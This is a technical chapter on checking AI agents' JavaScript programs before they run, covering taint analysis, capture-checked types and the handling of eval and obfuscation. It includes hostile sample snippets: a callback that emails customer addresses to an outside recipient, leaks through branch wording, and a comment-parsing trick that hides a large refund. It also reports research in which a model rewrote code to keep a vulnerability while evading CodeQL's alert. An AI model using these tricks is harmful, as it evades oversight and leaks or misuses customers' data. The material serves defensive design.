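Taint analysis traces whether data from a named source can reach a named destination. Meijer's rule against sending fetched mail outside the company is a typical use. For the program above, the source is the result of `listOrders` and the destination is the `body` of `sendEmail`. The analysis marks the source and then follows the mark through the code:

```
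orders            marked, because it holds the result of listOrders
o                 marked, because map passes each order to its function
o.customerEmail   marked, because it is part of a marked order
emails            marked, because map collects the function's results
text              marked, because + copies both sides into the result
body              marked, because it holds text, so the data has arrived
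```

Assignments and property reads are simple to follow. For built-in functions, taint analysis needs a description of each one, as pointer analysis does. This description, called a summary, covers how data gets from the function's inputs to its outputs. The shop's subset needs only a few:

| Expression | Where the data goes |
|---|---|
| `a + b` | From both sides into the result |
| `list.slice(0, n)` | From the items into the new list |
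| `list.map(f)` | From each item into the parameter of `f`, and from the result of `f` into the new list |
| `list.filter(f)` | From each item into the parameter of `f`, and from the items into the new list |
| `list.length` | From the list into the number |

The shop's rule allows text from an order to go to the customer who placed that order, so the checker has to record which order each piece of data came from. If it gave everything from `listOrders` the same mark and banned all marked data from emails, it would reject the shop's normal program, which puts `order.id` in the subject line. In that program, both `order.id` and `order.customerEmail` come from the constant `order`, which holds one record during each pass through the loop. In the harmful program, `text` may contain data from any order, so the checker rejects the program. The rule should cover `subject` as well as `body`, since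 a subject line can carry the same list.

To protect integrity, the checker needs marks on individual fields. Customers supply their own email addresses, so a rule that kept all customer-supplied data out of `to` would stop the shop from emailing them. The shop can accept an order's `customerEmail` as an address for messages about that order and refuse every other field. The checker can't tell whether someone has tampered with `customerEmail` in the shop's records, so the shop has to protect that field itself.

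The program's return value is a destination too, and an easy one to overlook. The host passes it to the model, which may use it when it writes the next program. If the first program returned the list of addresses, the second could contain them as fixed text:

```js
await api.sendEmail({ to: order.customerEmail, subject: "Refund", body: "ana@mail.example, ben@mail.example" });
```

A checker that reads only this program finds a harmless constant. Odersky and colleagues describe the same gap in systems that track taint while a program runs, because the taint marks disappear once a value enters the model's context as ordinary language. The shop's normal program avoids the problem by returning two counts. The checker could require every program to return only numbers, though a long list of numbers could still encode a message.

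### Flows through conditions

The flows so far are direct, which means that the program copies data or computes a new value from it. A program can also reveal data indirectly, by letting it decide what happens next:

```js
for (const order of late.slice(0, 1)) {
  await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
  for (const other of orders.slice(0, 1)) {
    if (other.total > 100) {
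      await api.sendEmail({ to: order.customerEmail, subject: "Refund", body: "Thank you!" });
    } else {
      await api.sendEmail({ to: order.customerEmail, subject: "Refund", body: "Thank you." });
    }
  }
}
```

Both email bodies are constants, so a taint analysis that follows only direct flows finds nothing wrong. But the recipient can tell from the exclamation mark that the first order of the week was over 100. A program with a thousand branches, each with its own wording, could reveal an exact amount in one email.

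Many tools ignore leaks through control flow. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which defines a small formal language for agents' programs, discusses FIDES, a defence that labels the data an agent reads. The paper notes that FIDES's confidentiality guarantee does not cover control flow that depends on data, and that leaks through control flow can be efficient.

The standard fix is to treat everything inside a branch as if it contained the data in the condition. Both emails above would then carry a mark from `other`, and the checker would reject the program because the recipient comes from `order`.

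But this remedy would reject the shop's normal program if it were applied everywhere. Its filter uses the dates to decide who gets an email, and `slice(0, 10)` makes the eleventh late customer's email depend on the ten orders before it. The checker could apply the strict rule to `if` statements and exempt filters and slices, but a hostile program could then move its condition into a filter and send an email only if the filtered list isn't empty.

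A workable compromise is for the shop to decide which fields a program can use in conditions and filters. Programs need dates and totals to choose orders, so the shop can allow those and accept that a hostile program could leak a little about them. It can ban more sensitive fields, such as addresses or the items bought, from conditions and filters. The limit of ten emails per task also restricts how much a program can leak this way.

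### How taint tools lose track of data

According to *Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (2026), existing taint tools for JavaScript typically look for flows found in web applications, such as from a request's parameters to a database query, and agents need their own list of sources and destinations. The tools therefore need changes to do this job, but the list for the shop is short.

Missing summaries of library functions are a bigger weakness. When CodeQL, the analysis tool behind GitHub's code scanning, has no summary for a library call, it treats the call as passing no taint. This reduces false alarms and lets the tool handle large programs, but the analysis loses track of any tainted data that does pass through the call.

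In *Preserve the Vulnerability, Break the Alert*, Cao, Ding and Xu (2026) measured how easily this happens. They started with 172 flows that CodeQL had correctly reported in npm packages with known vulnerabilities. For each flow, they showed a language model the alert and asked it to rewrite one function so that the vulnerability remained, the change looked like routine maintenance and the alert disappeared. They didn't show the model how CodeQL works. Three independent attempts at each flow produced 514 valid rewrites. The researchers checked by hand whether the vulnerability had survived.

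At least one attempt succeeded for 26.2% of the flows, and each hidden flow cost about $0.51. In a comparison run, the same model refactored the same functions without seeing the alert or knowing about the vulnerability, and none of those 516 rewrites hid a flow.

The comparison suggests that a model writing ordinary code will rarely hide a flow by accident, at least when CodeQL would have caught the flow written in the usual way. But a checker that returns its reasons for rejecting a program gives the model much the same information as the alerts in the main experiment. A hostile model could use those reasons to search for a gap. Even a model that isn't hostile might keep changing a program until the checker stops reporting the flow, without removing it.

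A checker can avoid this weakness by assuming the opposite, that data from every input of an unknown function may reach every output. Kishor, Nicolet and Dodds (2026), in *Soundness Checking of Taint Flow Models*, call this the most-general summary. It is sound by construction but causes more false alarms. In their work at Amazon Web Services, they aim for summaries that are both sound and more precise by having a language model propose each summary and a separate algorithm try to prove it sound.

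One of their examples is a function in the language Go that receives a web request and a logger, writes to the log and returns an error if something goes wrong. The model proposes that data flows only from the request to the logger. The algorithm lists every other possible flow and tries to rule each one out:

```
request → returned error    impossible: the error is always empty or a fixed message
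logger  → returned error    impossible for the same reason
logger  → request           impossible: the only inner function given both
                            never writes to the request
```

The algorithm uses quick checks like these, on types and on which memory a function reads or writes. When they aren't enough, it works out what would have to be true of the functions that function calls, and checks each of them in turn. It therefore rarely has to trace data through all the code.

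Kishor and colleagues tested 97 summaries from six Go codebases. Some described an interface with many implementations, so the summaries covered 2,535 methods, and the algorithm proved them sound for 93% of these. It found no proof for about 5%. For the other 2%, it ruled out the forbidden flows, but the code used features, such as reflection, that could invalidate the result. The taint analysis produced no extra false alarms with these summaries. Without them, it timed out after 30 minutes on three of the six codebases, but with them it finished each in under four minutes, including the proofs.

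The 93% makes the problem look easier than it is, because for more than 2,000 of the methods the model proposed the most-general summary, which needs no further proof. The method also depends on Go's type system, ignores flows through conditions and can't handle summaries for functions that take other functions as arguments. JavaScript programs often use such functions, including `map` and `filter`. The shop is better off using a handful of summaries that a person writes and tests, and the most-general summary for anything it adds later.

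### Putting permissions in types

Another approach uses a programming language whose compiler rejects forbidden data flows. The restricted Scala of Odersky and colleagues, mentioned earlier, works this way. Their system, TACIT, uses capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3.

TACIT's programs act on the outside world through capabilities, which are values that a program must hold to perform an operation. A file handle is one example. Capture checking adds a capture set to a value's type, listing the capabilities that the value may use. Suppose `mailer` is the capability to send email. Two functions on orders would have these types:

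```scala
(o: Order) => o.total                       // Order -> Int
(o: Order) => mailer.send(o.email, "Hi")    // Order ->{mailer} Unit
```

The first function is pure, meaning it holds no capabilities. It can compute a result but can't send, write or print anything. The compiler infers that the second function's type includes `mailer`, even if the model doesn't declare it.

TACIT keeps sensitive data in a wrapper called `Classified`. A program can't open the wrapper. It can only pass a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies the function to the contents and wraps the result. The method accepts only pure functions:

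```scala
val orders: Classified[List[Order]] = listOrders(week)

orders.map(list => list.count(o => o.isLate))           // accepted
orders.map(list => mailer.send(eve, list.toString))     // rejected
```

The count in the first call is also `Classified`. This also blocks the leak through conditions. Code outside the wrapper can't branch on the data because it never has it. A function inside can branch on the data but can affect only its own wrapped result.

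The program can write wrapped data to a protected file, print it, or pass it to a second, trusted model running locally. If it prints the data, the user sees the real contents, but the agent's model receives only `Classified(****)`. The local model's answer comes back wrapped. An agent can therefore have a confidential contract summarised without reading it, so it can't copy the contents into its next program as fixed text.

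The types record what each function may use, so the compiler can check each function separately instead of tracing data through the whole program. But ordinary Scala code can evade the types through features such as unchecked casts, which tell the compiler to treat a value as another type, and reflection, which finds functions by name while the program runs. TACIT compiles the agent's code in a safe mode that forbids these features. Safe mode also limits programs to library code that is itself safe. A developer can mark other library code as safe, and the compiler doesn't check that it is.

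Some checks still happen at run time. For instance, a program asks for access to a folder and receives a capability that the compiler confines to one block of code. If the program then tries to open a file outside that folder, the library stops it with an error.

### What the tests of TACIT found

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of secrets, such as passwords for online services. They paired each of 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets outright or pretended to have the authority to see them. They ran all 131 trials with two models, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

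| Trials with no leak | Secrets wrapped | Secrets as plain text |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 100% | 91.6% |

Most of the leaks came from the 11 requests by a malicious user. MiniMax M2.5 leaked secrets in eight of them, and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in two. The prompt injections succeeded three times, all against MiniMax. With the secrets wrapped, the agents completed 99.2% and 90.0% of the ordinary tasks, one slightly more and the other considerably more than without wrapping.

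The type system should guarantee this perfect score, so the trials mainly test whether TACIT implements the type system correctly. They include injected Scala code meant to read the secrets, but the set of attacks was fixed, and a determined attacker would look for bugs in the compiler or the library.

Any loss in performance was small. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a retailer, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when they wrote Scala than when they called tools directly. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to the clearer types and the compiler's error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real software bugs, MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without. These figures include retries after compiler errors, which a later section covers.

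TACIT has several stated limits. It doesn't check whether a program does the right thing. A function can leak a little information through timing, for example by running longer when the wrapped data has a certain property. If a program is allowed to start external commands, the type system can't control what those commands do. Earlier work has proved the core of capture checking sound, but there is not yet a proof that safe mode provides its intended guarantees.

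### LACUNA and ETAS

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) extends this approach to agents that write code in the middle of a running program. A developer leaves a gap in the program and states what type of value belongs there. When execution reaches the gap, a model writes code to fill it, and the compiler checks that code against the surrounding program before any of it runs. The code can use only the capabilities available at that point.

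LACUNA reduced task success more than TACIT did. On a larger set of τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. The paper calls this "on par", but a 14-point gap would matter to a shop. A weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, solved 29.1% with LACUNA and 33.2% with ordinary tool calls.

Attacks also succeeded in seven of 949 prompt-injection trials with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues explain that the compiler can't stop an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a capability the task needs. The shop's assistant needs to send email, so a capability for email alone wouldn't protect it. The data also needs a wrapper or a flow rule.

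*ETAS* (Tan, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a new language for agents, instead checks which operations a program requests and in what order. Each function declares the operations it may request, and a specification can, for example, require a request for approval before any request to change a file. The compiler proves that the specification holds where it can and adds a run-time monitor where it can't. In a small test of six programs, it accepted the two valid ones and rejected the four that contained errors.

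These checks don't cover where data goes. In the shop, ETAS could require a refund before each email, but the program that mails out everyone's address would still pass. So its checks would complement a taint analysis or a wrapper but couldn't replace one.

### Why TypeScript's types are not enough

TypeScript adds types to JavaScript, and models write it fluently, so it is tempting to use its compiler as the checker. But its types describe the shape of data and not what a function may do. Suppose a host function accepts any function that takes an order and returns text:

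```ts
function describe(order: Order, f: (o: Order) => string): string {
  return f(order);
}

describe(order, o => {
  api.sendEmail({ to: "eve@mail.example", subject: "Order", body: o.customerEmail });
  return "done";
});
```

TypeScript accepts this because the function takes an order and returns text. The type can't record that the function also sends an email. Tan and colleagues make the same point about agent frameworks in general, where parameter and return types don't show which operations a workflow may request. In Scala with capture checking, `describe` could require a pure function, and the compiler would reject the call.

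A developer could write a `Classified` wrapper in TypeScript, but programs could get around its types. The type `any` switches off checking for a value, and a cast can turn almost any type into another. A template string accepts a value of any type and converts it to text, so the wrapper would have to hide its contents at runtime. Odersky and colleagues write that another mainstream language would need to add capability tracking and restrict its features to guarantee purity, and they expect this to take longer than starting from Scala.

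### What a JavaScript system could borrow

The shop can get part of TACIT's protection without new types. The shop's JavaScript subset already forbids `api` calls in functions passed to `filter` and `map`. Since `api` is the only capability in the program, those functions are pure, and the checker can confirm this from the syntax tree.

The shop can also copy the idea behind the wrapper by keeping sensitive data out of the program. `listOrders` could return each order's number, dates and total, but no address. A new host function would then look up the address and send the message:

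```js
for (const order of small.slice(0, 10)) {
  await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
  await api.sendRefundNotice({ orderId: order.id });
}
```

The program can no longer leak an address, directly or through a condition, because it never receives one. It also can't set an email's recipient or body, so the two flow rules about emails become unnecessary. The host only has to check that the task has refunded the order. If the program needs to group orders by customer, the host can supply a random label for each customer instead of the address.

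A host can also check labels at run time. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes a Haskell system that raises a computation's label as it reads restricted data, and checks the label before each operation with an outside effect. This needs no analysis of the program's text, but one label for the whole computation is too coarse for the shop. Once a program had read the orders, the label would cover every customer's data, and the host would have to refuse every email or make an exception.

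Fixed notices work for refunds, but a reply to a complaint may need details from the customer's order and wording that fits the case. Like TACIT, the shop could use a second model. A host function would give that model one order and one complaint, with no access to tools or other orders, and send its reply only to that customer. The reply might still be wrong or rude, but it couldn't contain another customer's data unless the complaint or the order already did.

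## Code built at run time and obfuscated code

The checker has to find every call a program makes, but with some JavaScript features, which function the program calls, or even what code it runs, depends on values known only at run time. A checker can reject any program that uses such a feature, resolve the feature (work out from the program's text everything the feature could do), or accept the program and have the host guard against misuse at run time.

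### Names worked out at run time

Computed property access is the most common of these features, and it is often harmless:

```js
const field = late.length > 10 ? "deposit" : "total";
const amount = order[field];
```

A checker can resolve this example because `field` has only two possible values. If `field` came from the order data, `order[field]` could be any property of the order, including the ones every object inherits from JavaScript's built-in objects. Kashyap and colleagues found that a single lookup with an unknown name could bring many built-in functions into their analysis. They reduced the problem by treating the names of built-in properties, such as `toString`, as a separate category, so the analysis can record that an unknown name isn't one of them.

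Resolving computed names this way takes a lot of code, and short programs rarely need them. The example can be written as `late.length > 10 ? order.deposit : order.total`, so the shop can reject computed names and have the model write that instead.

Totals for each customer are harder to rewrite, because the names come from the data. Earlier, the shop needed a helper function for them. It could instead add JavaScript's `Map` to the subset and permit only its `get` and `set` methods:

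```js
totals.set(order.customerEmail, 20);
const sum = totals.get(order.customerEmail);
```

A `Map` stores its entries separately from its properties, so an entry named `constructor` doesn't lead to a built-in function. The checker doesn't need the entries' names, but it must allow for `get` returning any value the program has stored in the `Map`.

The obsolete `with` statement makes even ordinary names uncertain:

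```js
const total = 20;
with (order) { return total; }
```

This returns the order's own `total` if it has one, and 20 if it doesn't. The checker can no longer link a name to its declaration, and inside the braces even `api` might refer to a field of the order. No program needs `with`, so the checker can safely reject it. JavaScript's strict mode already forbids it, so a checker that parses programs as strict code needs no extra rule, provided the host also runs them as strict code.

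### Code that isn't in the text

With `eval` and the `Function` constructor, a program can turn a string into code:

```js
const five = eval("2 + 3");
const double = new Function("x", "return x * 2");
```

Both strings are fixed here, so a checker could parse them as part of the program. If the program assembles a string as it runs, the checker can't determine which operations the resulting code will perform. It also can't rely on its earlier conclusions about the rest of the program, because code run by a direct call to `eval` can change variables in the surrounding scope.

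Kashyap and colleagues list several ways to handle `eval`. An analyser can disallow it, or a tool can rewrite programs to remove it. The analyser can also make assumptions about what the string will do and have the runtime enforce them, for example in a sandbox. The last option is to analyse the new code when it appears during the run. Kashyap and colleagues disallow `eval`, and their analyser prints a warning if a program might call it.

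The shop should reject `eval` too, and the host should disable it in case the checker has a bug. Banning the word isn't enough, because web pages can turn text into code in other ways. Richards, Hammer and colleagues, in *The Eval that Men Do*, count eight ways in all, including timers that accept a string and changes to the page's script elements. On the 100 popular sites they browsed by hand, pages used the `Function` constructor more often than `eval`. The shop's list of permitted names excludes all eight.

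A program can also bring in code from elsewhere:

```js
const name = "date-tools";
const tools = await import(name);
```

If the name of an imported module is unknown, the module's contents are unknown too. Xu and Møller consider importing such a module about as dangerous as running computed text, because it may contain code that nobody has analysed. The shop's programs need no modules, so its checker can reject every import. A host that offers packages can require programs to write package names as fixed text, as NCP does.

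### Functions that run without a visible call

As mentioned earlier, a program can run functions that it never visibly calls. A getter is one way:

```js
const cart = { get total() { return 5 + 3; } };
const price = cart.total;
```

A setter also runs a function when a program assigns a value to a property. A checker that looks only for calls would miss the function that runs on the second line.

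A changed prototype gives every object of one kind a new method, or replaces an existing one:

```js
Array.prototype.first = function () { return this[0]; };
const earliest = orders.first();
```

The second line is visibly a call, but the checker can't tell from that line which function it runs.

Implicit conversion can call a function during ordinary arithmetic:

```js
const price = { valueOf() { return 20; } };
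const sum = price + 5;
```

Kashyap and colleagues handle these conversions by translating JavaScript into a simpler language in which each conversion is a separate step. The shop doesn't need this translation. All three examples put a function into an object, which its subset forbids, and the host prevents the same problem in objects from outside the program by supplying plain data and freezing prototypes.

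### What static analysers miss

Chakraborty, Olivares and colleagues (2022), in *Automatic Root Cause Quantification for Missing Edges in JavaScript Call Graphs*, measured how often such features cause an analyser to miss a call. They ran ten versions of the same to-do list application, eight of them built with different web frameworks, and recorded every call. They compared these calls with a static analyser's call graph of the code.

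To find out why a call was missing, they also recorded each time the running program created, stored, read or called a function. Suppose a program stores a function in the `thank` property of an object and calls it like this:

```js
const replies = { thank: sayThanks };
replies["th" + "ank"]();
```

The analyser tracks `sayThanks` into the property but does not connect the property to the call. The method finds this missing connection by working backwards from the call and attributes it to computed property access.

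Chakraborty and colleagues tested two versions of the analyser. At first, 24% of the calls missed by the more thorough version went to built-in functions that the analyser had no description of. After they added many of the missing descriptions, this version found 76% of the calls that really happened. Computed property access caused 70% of the remaining misses, and code created with the `Function` constructor caused 10%. The second most common cause was the `Function` constructor for React, and getters and setters for Vue.

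The simpler version found only 37% of the calls, mostly because it didn't follow functions that a program passes to or returns from other functions. The thorough version did follow them, but fewer than 5% of the calls it predicted in the React application occurred during the test. On a larger application called Juice Shop, the thorough version ran out of memory at 64 gigabytes.

A checker that misses a quarter of a program's calls would be useless for controlling refunds, but the shop's JavaScript subset excludes most of the causes of these misses. Chakraborty and colleagues also examined how the programs computed the property names that led to the missed calls. The last column of the table lists suggested alternatives for a short program.

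| Where the name came from | Share | Plainer alternative |
|---|---|---|
| A loop over all of an object's properties | 31% | Write out the fields the task needs |
| A parameter of the function | 28% | Read the named property before calling the function |
| Strings joined together | 14% | Write the full name, or use a list |
| A variable from an enclosing function | 12% | Read the named property where the program chooses it |
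| Another property | 12% | Use a `Map` |

Web frameworks use computed names to work with objects whose fields their authors can't know in advance. A model writing for the shop has a description of every field, so it has much less need for computed names. The percentages may not apply to model-written scripts, since each framework appeared in only one small application.

### How websites used `eval`

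In March 2011, Richards and colleagues recorded 550,358 calls to `eval` on more than 10,000 sites. Of the 100 most popular sites, 82% used it, as did about half of the 10,000 most popular, so a scanner that rejected every page containing `eval` would have rejected many of the most popular sites.

Most of these calls didn't need `eval`. Many sites used it to read JSON data, although JavaScript already had a function for that. The German news site heute.de used it to find a browser's Flash plugin version. The page created ten variables with names such as `flash8Installed`, then built each name in a loop and passed it to `eval` to read the variable. The page already had the version number, so a single assignment would have been enough.

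On the sites Richards and colleagues operated by hand, 76% of the strings passed to `eval` fell into categories that programmers could mostly replace with ordinary JavaScript. Individual uses were also predictable, since only 1.4% of the places in the code that called `eval` passed it strings from more than one category. The follow-up paper *Eval begone!* describes Evalorizer, a tool that helps programmers remove unneeded `eval` calls.

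More recently, Xu and Møller studied npm packages instead of websites. They found that 228 of 9,082 packages (about 2.5%) ran computed text as code or used a related feature such as WebAssembly. Another 203 passed a fixed string to `eval` or `Function`, often just to detect their runtime environment.

The remaining uses of `eval` are harder to replace. Some of the websites used it to load whole libraries, and others ran code that fitted no category. A program that makes refunds doesn't need to do either, so the shop loses very little by banning `eval`.

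### Running parts of the code to fill the gaps

Some facts that are hard to work out from the text become obvious once the code runs. Express, a popular library for web servers, gives its application object methods called `get`, `post` and so on by looping over a list of names. In simplified form:

```js
for (const method of methods) {
  app[method] = function (path) { /* ... */ };
}
```

Express uses a loop to define methods such as `app.get` under computed names, so a static analyser that ignores computed names won't find them. The loop sets them up in the same way every time, so running it once reveals them all.

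Laursen, Xu and Møller automate this in *Reducing Static Analysis Unsoundness with Approximate Interpretation* (2024). Their tool loads each module and then runs functions it defines, including many that an ordinary test run wouldn't reach. Because the arguments those functions expect are unknown, the tool passes a stand-in object that accepts any operation. Reading a property of the stand-in returns the same stand-in, and calling it does nothing. The tool replaces functions for files, networking and starting processes with harmless substitutes, and it stops code that loops for too long.

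While the code runs, the tool records hints. For example, it might record that the object created on line 35 received a `get` property holding the function from line 38. The static analyser adds these hints to what it inferred from the source text. Some hints may be wrong, because the stand-in can make the code take a path that no real run would take.

On 36 projects with recorded calls for comparison, the average share of real calls that appeared in the call graph rose from 75.9% to 88.1%, while precision fell by only 1.5%. The share rose from 40.1% to 98.0% for the web framework Connect, but only from 37.1% to 41.6% for Kraken, another web framework, partly because computed module names still hid entire modules. Running the code took an average of 4.5 seconds per program.

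This is a large improvement for finding bugs, but it doesn't make the analyser sound. On average, the analyser still missed about 12% of the calls, and the tool ran only 60% of the functions. A hostile program could also behave differently when it receives a stand-in instead of real data. The lack of a hint is therefore not enough reason to accept a program.

It is also odd to run parts of an untrusted program to decide whether it is safe to run. The substitutes reduce the risk, but the tool would still need proper isolation. The technique seems more useful for the host's own libraries, which are larger, change less often, and aren't written to deceive anyone.

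Xu and Møller's later capability analysis covers the same gaps with indirect reports that don't depend on guesses, so a checker can base a guarantee on them.

### Kinds of obfuscation

Obfuscation means rewriting code to make it hard to understand without changing its behaviour. Companies use it to protect their code from copying, and attackers use it to hide malicious code. *Nowhere to Hide* (2022), a paper on detecting scripts that identify visitors by their browsers, distinguishes obfuscation from minification, which makes code smaller so that pages load faster. The two can look alike because minifiers also shorten names and remove spaces.

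| Kind | What it does | What it can hide from a checker |
|---|---|---|
| Renaming | Replaces names such as `orders` with `a` | Nothing |
| Encoded strings | Stores text in scrambled form and decodes it during the run | Property names and arguments |
| Flattened control flow | Puts the program's steps into one loop, with a variable that selects the next step | The order and number of calls |
| Run-time unpacking | Stores the program as text and turns it back into code during the run | Every operation |

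Renaming doesn't matter to a checker of operations. The first two lines of the shop's program could look like this:

```js
const a = await api.listOrders({ from: "2026-11-23", to: "2026-11-29" });
const b = a.filter(c => c.deliveredOn > c.promisedOn);
```

The checker links each name to its declaration, so it makes no difference whether the list is called `orders` or `a`. The names `api`, `listOrders` and those of an order's fields do matter, but the host defines them, so renaming them would break the program.

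Converting a script to a standard form can remove differences introduced by obfuscation. The classifier in *Towards Seamless Tracking-Free Web* (2016) does this first. In the paper's example, an online obfuscator renamed the variables in a tracking script from the advertising company Criteo and removed its white space. After conversion, the original and obfuscated versions were identical.

Encoded strings matter when they hide the name of an operation or an argument. The shop's subset prevents them from hiding an operation's name by rejecting computed names, and it has no functions for decoding text. If the shop added one, the checker would have to treat the decoded result as unknown text. The checker would reject that text as an email address but allow it in a subject line, where the scope permits "any text". The person approving the task couldn't tell what the email would say, so the shop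 should require fixed text or named fields in the subject line. A sound taint analysis still works on encoded text, because the text keeps the mark of the data it came from.

Flattening is easiest to understand from an outline:

```
step = 1
while step is not 0:
    if step is 1:        refund the order, then set step to 2
    otherwise:           email the customer, then set step to 0
```

This flattened program makes one refund and then sends one email. A checker can't establish this if it assumes that a loop may repeat any number of times and that either branch may run. It has to allow for unlimited refunds and for an email before the refund, so it rejects the program. Flattening therefore makes permitted operations harder to prove safe, but it can't get a forbidden operation past a sound checker.

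The same applies to the redundant instructions that some obfuscators insert. If they include an `api` call that never runs, the checker still adds it to the list of operations, which may cause a false rejection.

Run-time unpacking hides the most and has been common on the web. *Nowhere to Hide* describes an earlier study of the 100,000 most popular websites, which found that nearly 90% of the scripts identified as obfuscated came from a single tool, DaftLogic, and concluded that `eval`-based obfuscation was the most common kind. The shop's ban on `eval` covers this kind with no need to recognise an obfuscator's style.

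### Detecting and undoing obfuscation

Security companies and browser makers can't always reject such code, so researchers have built tools to detect it. *Nowhere to Hide* describes two earlier approaches. One is to train machine-learning classifiers to recognise obfuscated and minified scripts. The other is to compare what static analysis finds in a script with what the script does when it runs, since a large difference suggests hidden behaviour.

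Neither approach would help the shop much. A classifier might flag harmless minified code and might miss a single encoded string in an otherwise tidy program. Comparing the text with a real run would mean making the refunds before the code had been checked. A checker of operations only has to determine whether it can account for every call, however strange the code looks.

Deobfuscation tools try to make obfuscated code readable again. *JsDeObsBench* (2025) compares language models on this task with existing tools such as Synchrony and JSNice, and tests whether the output has valid syntax and passes execution checks. These tests are necessary because a model can produce a clear, plausible program that behaves differently from the original. Obfuscators can also change a program's behaviour, and *OBsmith* (2025) uses language models to test whether they do.

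The original programs in JsDeObsBench are at most 2,048 tokens long, so they are closer in length to an agent's script than to the code of a large website. Even so, a host shouldn't approve an unreadable program just because a model's translation of it looks harmless. If the translation leaves out one call, the host will run a call that the checker never examined. It would be safer to discard the original, then check and run the translation. A mistake in translation might then spoil the task, but it couldn't cause an unchecked operation to run. If the host is going to discard the original, though, it might as well ask for a new program.

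### Asking for a plain version

The main advantage of checking code that a model has just written is that the checker can ask for a new program. A company that scans a website's scripts usually has no contact with the people who wrote them. Blocking every script its scanner can't read would break pages that visitors may depend on, while allowing them all would let malicious ones through. The scanner therefore has to estimate what unreadable code does, and it will sometimes be wrong.

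Nobody depends on the shop's program yet, so the checker can reject it with a specific reason, such as "line 3 works out a property name at run time; write the name in full". (A later section covers these messages and the attempts that follow them.)

Analysers of existing code can't just reject a program that contains a construct they can't resolve, as the shop's checker can. Santra and colleagues' system, ACaM, analyses agents' existing tools, and a person has to investigate any construct it marks as unknown. They put obfuscated code outside the system's scope.

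An older, similar policy applies to browser add-ons. Kashyap and colleagues note that the official add-on repositories vet each submission and strongly discourage `eval`, and none of the 28 programs they tested used it. Developers accepted the restriction because they wanted their add-ons published.

The policy also works against a hostile model, because the checker rejects programs that hide operations. But it depends on how well the checker defines readable code, as the n8n flaws showed.

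### Minified libraries

A blanket rule against unreadable code causes problems when a program needs a minified library. For example, the model might copy a minified date library into its program to work out which orders were late. The short names are harmless, but libraries often use `this`, prototypes and computed names, so the checker would probably reject the unminified version too.

The shop could exempt the library from checking, but the model might have changed it while copying, deliberately or not. Loosening the subset for every program would be worse. It is safer for the host to provide the few date functions that programs need, so that programs don't have to include the library in their text.

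Somebody still has to review the library, but only once for each version. They should analyse the readable source and then minify it themselves, because a package's published minified file may not match its published source.

### Data that acts as code

Code that is neither malicious nor obfuscated can still let its input determine which functions it calls. Xu and Møller found an example in `@ungap/structured-clone`, a widely used npm package that rebuilds JavaScript objects from stored data. The data includes the name of each object's type, and the package uses that name to look up a built-in constructor through computed property access. An attacker who controls the data can name `Function`, the constructor that turns text into code.

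Xu and Møller wrote a small malicious package that used this weakness and gave GPT-5.2 its JavaScript, but not the separate data file containing the harmful text. The model wrongly reported no malicious behaviour. Xu and Møller acknowledge that it might have caught the attack with that file, or on another attempt, and newer models may do better. The example still shows that code looking harmless to a reader is weak evidence that it is safe. Their own analysis reported the two lines where the package looks up a constructor.

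The shop's subset forbids such lookups in the program, but a host function can reintroduce the problem:

```js
const task = { action: order.nextStep, orderId: order.id };
await api.run(task);
```

Even if the subset allowed this call, the checker would find only one operation, `run`, which could do anything the host supports. Whether the call issued a refund or sent an email would depend on the data in `nextStep`. AgentScript avoids this by requiring the name passed to `callTool` to be fixed text, and the shop does so by giving each operation its own function.

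Text in other languages raises the same issue. If the host offered `api.query({ sql: text })`, the text would be a program for the database, and a JavaScript checker couldn't tell a lookup from a deletion. Xu and Møller found a more extreme case in the npm package fengari, which runs programs written in the language Lua. A JavaScript analyser treats those programs only as data. The host should therefore offer specific functions, such as one that looks up a single order, or have a separate checker for the other language.

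### Plain code with a harmful purpose

Most malicious code doesn't need these features. Of the 1,311 malicious npm packages that Xu and Møller studied, 1,156 contained code to send data over the network, either directly or in their dependencies. Only 60 ran computed text as code or used a related feature such as WebAssembly. A rule against `eval` would not have blocked most of the packages, but a scope that forbade network requests would have stopped them from sending data that way.

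A scope can also miss mistakes, such as the `>=` one. A person reading a plain program could notice that kind of mistake, but it would be much harder to notice in a flattened or encoded version.

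## Running exactly what was checked

The checker's verdict applies only to the text it checked, parsed the same way and run with the same version of the host API and JavaScript's unmodified built-in functions. If any of these changes before the program runs, the host may run something the checker never approved.

### What can change after the check

Tools often change a program's text before it runs. Varda and colleagues describe a Cloudflare library that corrects common formatting errors in model-written code. OpenClaw's *Code Mode internals*, which documents a system for running AI agents, describes a step that converts TypeScript to JavaScript. Even wrapping a program in a function, so that it can use `await` and `return`, changes the text. If these steps come after the check, the engine runs text that hasn't been checked. The host should make all its changes first, check the result and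 keep that exact copy to run.

The checker's parser and the JavaScript engine can also read the same text differently. For example, under the JavaScript standard, `<!--` starts a comment in an ordinary script but is three operators in a module: less than, not, and subtract one.

```js
for (const order of late.slice(0, 1)) {
  const x = 0 <!--order.total || await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: 5000 })
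}
```

A checker that parses this as a script finds `const x = 0` and a comment, both harmless. In a module, the same line subtracts one from the order's total and makes a comparison. For an order of 30 the comparison is false, so the code to the right of `||` runs and refunds 5,000. V8, the engine in Chrome and Node.js, rejects `<!--` in modules, but an engine that follows the standard exactly would make the refund. A checker can't always assume a particular engine, since OpenClaw can run a program on either Node or a smaller engine called QuickJS.

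Parsing in the same mode as the engine closes this gap. A more general remedy is for the host to print a new program from the checked syntax tree and run that. The printed program has no comments, so it omits anything the checker took for a comment.

The host API may change as well. Suppose an update makes `api.refund` add the delivery charge to every refund. A program approved for refunds of at most 50 could then pay out more. The host can give each version of the API an identifier, store it with the verdict, and check the program again if the identifier has changed.

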